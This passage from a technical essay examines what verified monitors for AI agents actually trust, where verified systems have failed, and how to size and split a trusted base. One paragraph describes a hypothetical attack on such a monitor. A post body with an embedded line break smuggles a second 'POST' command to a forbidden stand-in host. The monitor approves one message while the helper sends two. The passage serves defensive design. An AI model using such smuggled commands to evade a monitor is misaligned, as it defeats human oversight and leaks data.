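| Code that produces events or effects | yes | yes | yes | partly; more elsewhere in the paper |
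| Operating system | excluded as a limitation | no | yes | yes |
| Hardware | excluded as a limitation | no | no | no |
| Certificate authorities | no | no | no | yes |
| Model provider | no | no | no | yes |
| Human approvers | no | no | no | yes |

Some of these gaps reflect differences between the systems. PocketFlow's proof, for example, involves no human approval. Others are probably a matter of convention, since few authors state that they trust the processor. For an operator, a component excluded from the theorem matters as much as one listed as trusted, because the guarantee can fail in either case. Moon and Varshney exclude kernel and hardware faults in their limitations section, so someone who read only their list of trusted components would miss both.

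### Where verified systems have failed

Bugs found in older verified software suggest which entries deserve the most attention. *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca et al., 2017) reports 16 bugs in IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three systems in which several computers coordinate through a proved protocol. Eleven were in the unverified shims that connect proved code to the network and disk, three were in specifications, and two were in verification tools. None were in the proved protocols. One of the tool bugs caused a prover crash to count as a successful verification.

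Yang, Chen, Eide and Regehr reached a similar result for compilers in *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (2011). They used their program Csmith to generate random C programs, compiled each one with several compilers and compared the results. They reported more than 325 previously unknown bugs. One of the compilers was CompCert, whose developers had proved that most of its translation preserves a program's meaning. After about six processor-years of testing with Csmith, they had found no case in which the version then under development produced wrong code.

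The errors in earlier versions of CompCert were in parts the proof did not cover. Some were in the unverified code that reads C source. Two others made CompCert produce PowerPC instructions containing a number too large for its field, because CompCert's formal description of the processor omitted the limit. The assembler, which turns instructions into machine code, rejected those instructions.

Neither study measures how often verified software fails, and both cover only a few verified programs. Still, the faults were in the places one would check by following the third step of the procedure. Moon and Varshney's proof follows IronFleet's style and has the same kind of unverified shim, so their shim and parser are the natural places to look for errors.

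One of Verdi's shim bugs let a client inject commands, because the code that turned requests into text did not properly separate commands from data. The file agent could have a similar bug. Suppose the monitor passes each allowed post to a network helper as a line of text that begins with "POST". The model proposes a post to api.example.org whose body contains a line break, followed by "POST files.example.net" and another message. The monitor checks one post and records one Sent event, but the helper reads two commands and sends two messages, the second to a forbidden host.

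The proof about the monitor remains valid, and random tests might never generate such a body. The runtime could avoid the problem by stating the length of each body in advance, so that the helper never searches the text for commands. L3M proves a similar property for messages between agents. Each stored message occupies one line and cannot contain a line break, so its text cannot be read as a second message.

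### Measuring a trusted base

People usually measure a TCB in lines of code. This gives a rough idea of how much work a review would take, but the total depends on which components are counted. L3M's six C files may be short, but the Linux kernel on the same list has tens of millions of lines. Definitions should also be counted, since people have to read them as carefully as code.

A second measure is the width of the interface, which is the number of different requests the untrusted side can make. The file agent has two kinds of action, PocketFlow has four and Tether infers 11. L3M has 25 main classes of effect, but agent-written programs may use at most 11 of them. These counts can mislead too, because a single Run(command) action exposes more than all four of PocketFlow's actions together.

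Exposure to hostile input is probably the best guide to where errors will matter. Suppose the file agent has a 300-line parser and a 3,000-line start-up program that reads a fixed configuration. The parser processes every output of a model that an attacker may control, while the start-up program runs once on text that the operator wrote. A reviewer with limited time should start with the parser, even though it is a tenth of the size.

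More precise policies tend to make the trusted computing base both larger and more exposed. Marc Brooker of AWS acknowledges that Strands Box allows finer rules than a plain sandbox but requires more trusted code. A firewall can restrict which addresses an agent contacts without interpreting the content of its requests, but a gateway that applies rules to that content has to parse text that an attacker may partly control.

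Operators can limit the damage from an error in a trusted component by giving each clause of the policy its own TCB. For the file agent, a firewall outside the runtime could enforce the restriction to api.example.org, provided the service has its own address and the model's provider gets a separate channel. The monitor would enforce the limit of two posts and the ban on posting after reading the key. An error in the monitor's parser could then let the agent violate those two clauses, but its messages would still reach only the permitted host.

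The alternative is to give the agent less powerful tools. Eisenach and colleagues measured the effect on 37 tasks from Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of command-line work, using Claude Opus 5 and three attempts per task. L3M succeeded at least once on 41.7 per cent of tasks when the agent had a shell, and on 27.0 per cent when it had only tools whose effects could be undone by L3M or were limited by a token. Letting the agent write its own tools accounted for about 3 percentage points of the lower figure.

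Claude Code with all permission checks turned off reached 59.5 per cent. Eisenach and colleagues attribute its lead over L3M with a shell to their lack of tuning, which is plausible but untested. The comparison within L3M is more informative. Removing the shell reduced the number of successes by about a third, though 37 tasks allow only a rough estimate. An agent that only reads notes and posts two summaries would do its job equally well with the narrower interface.
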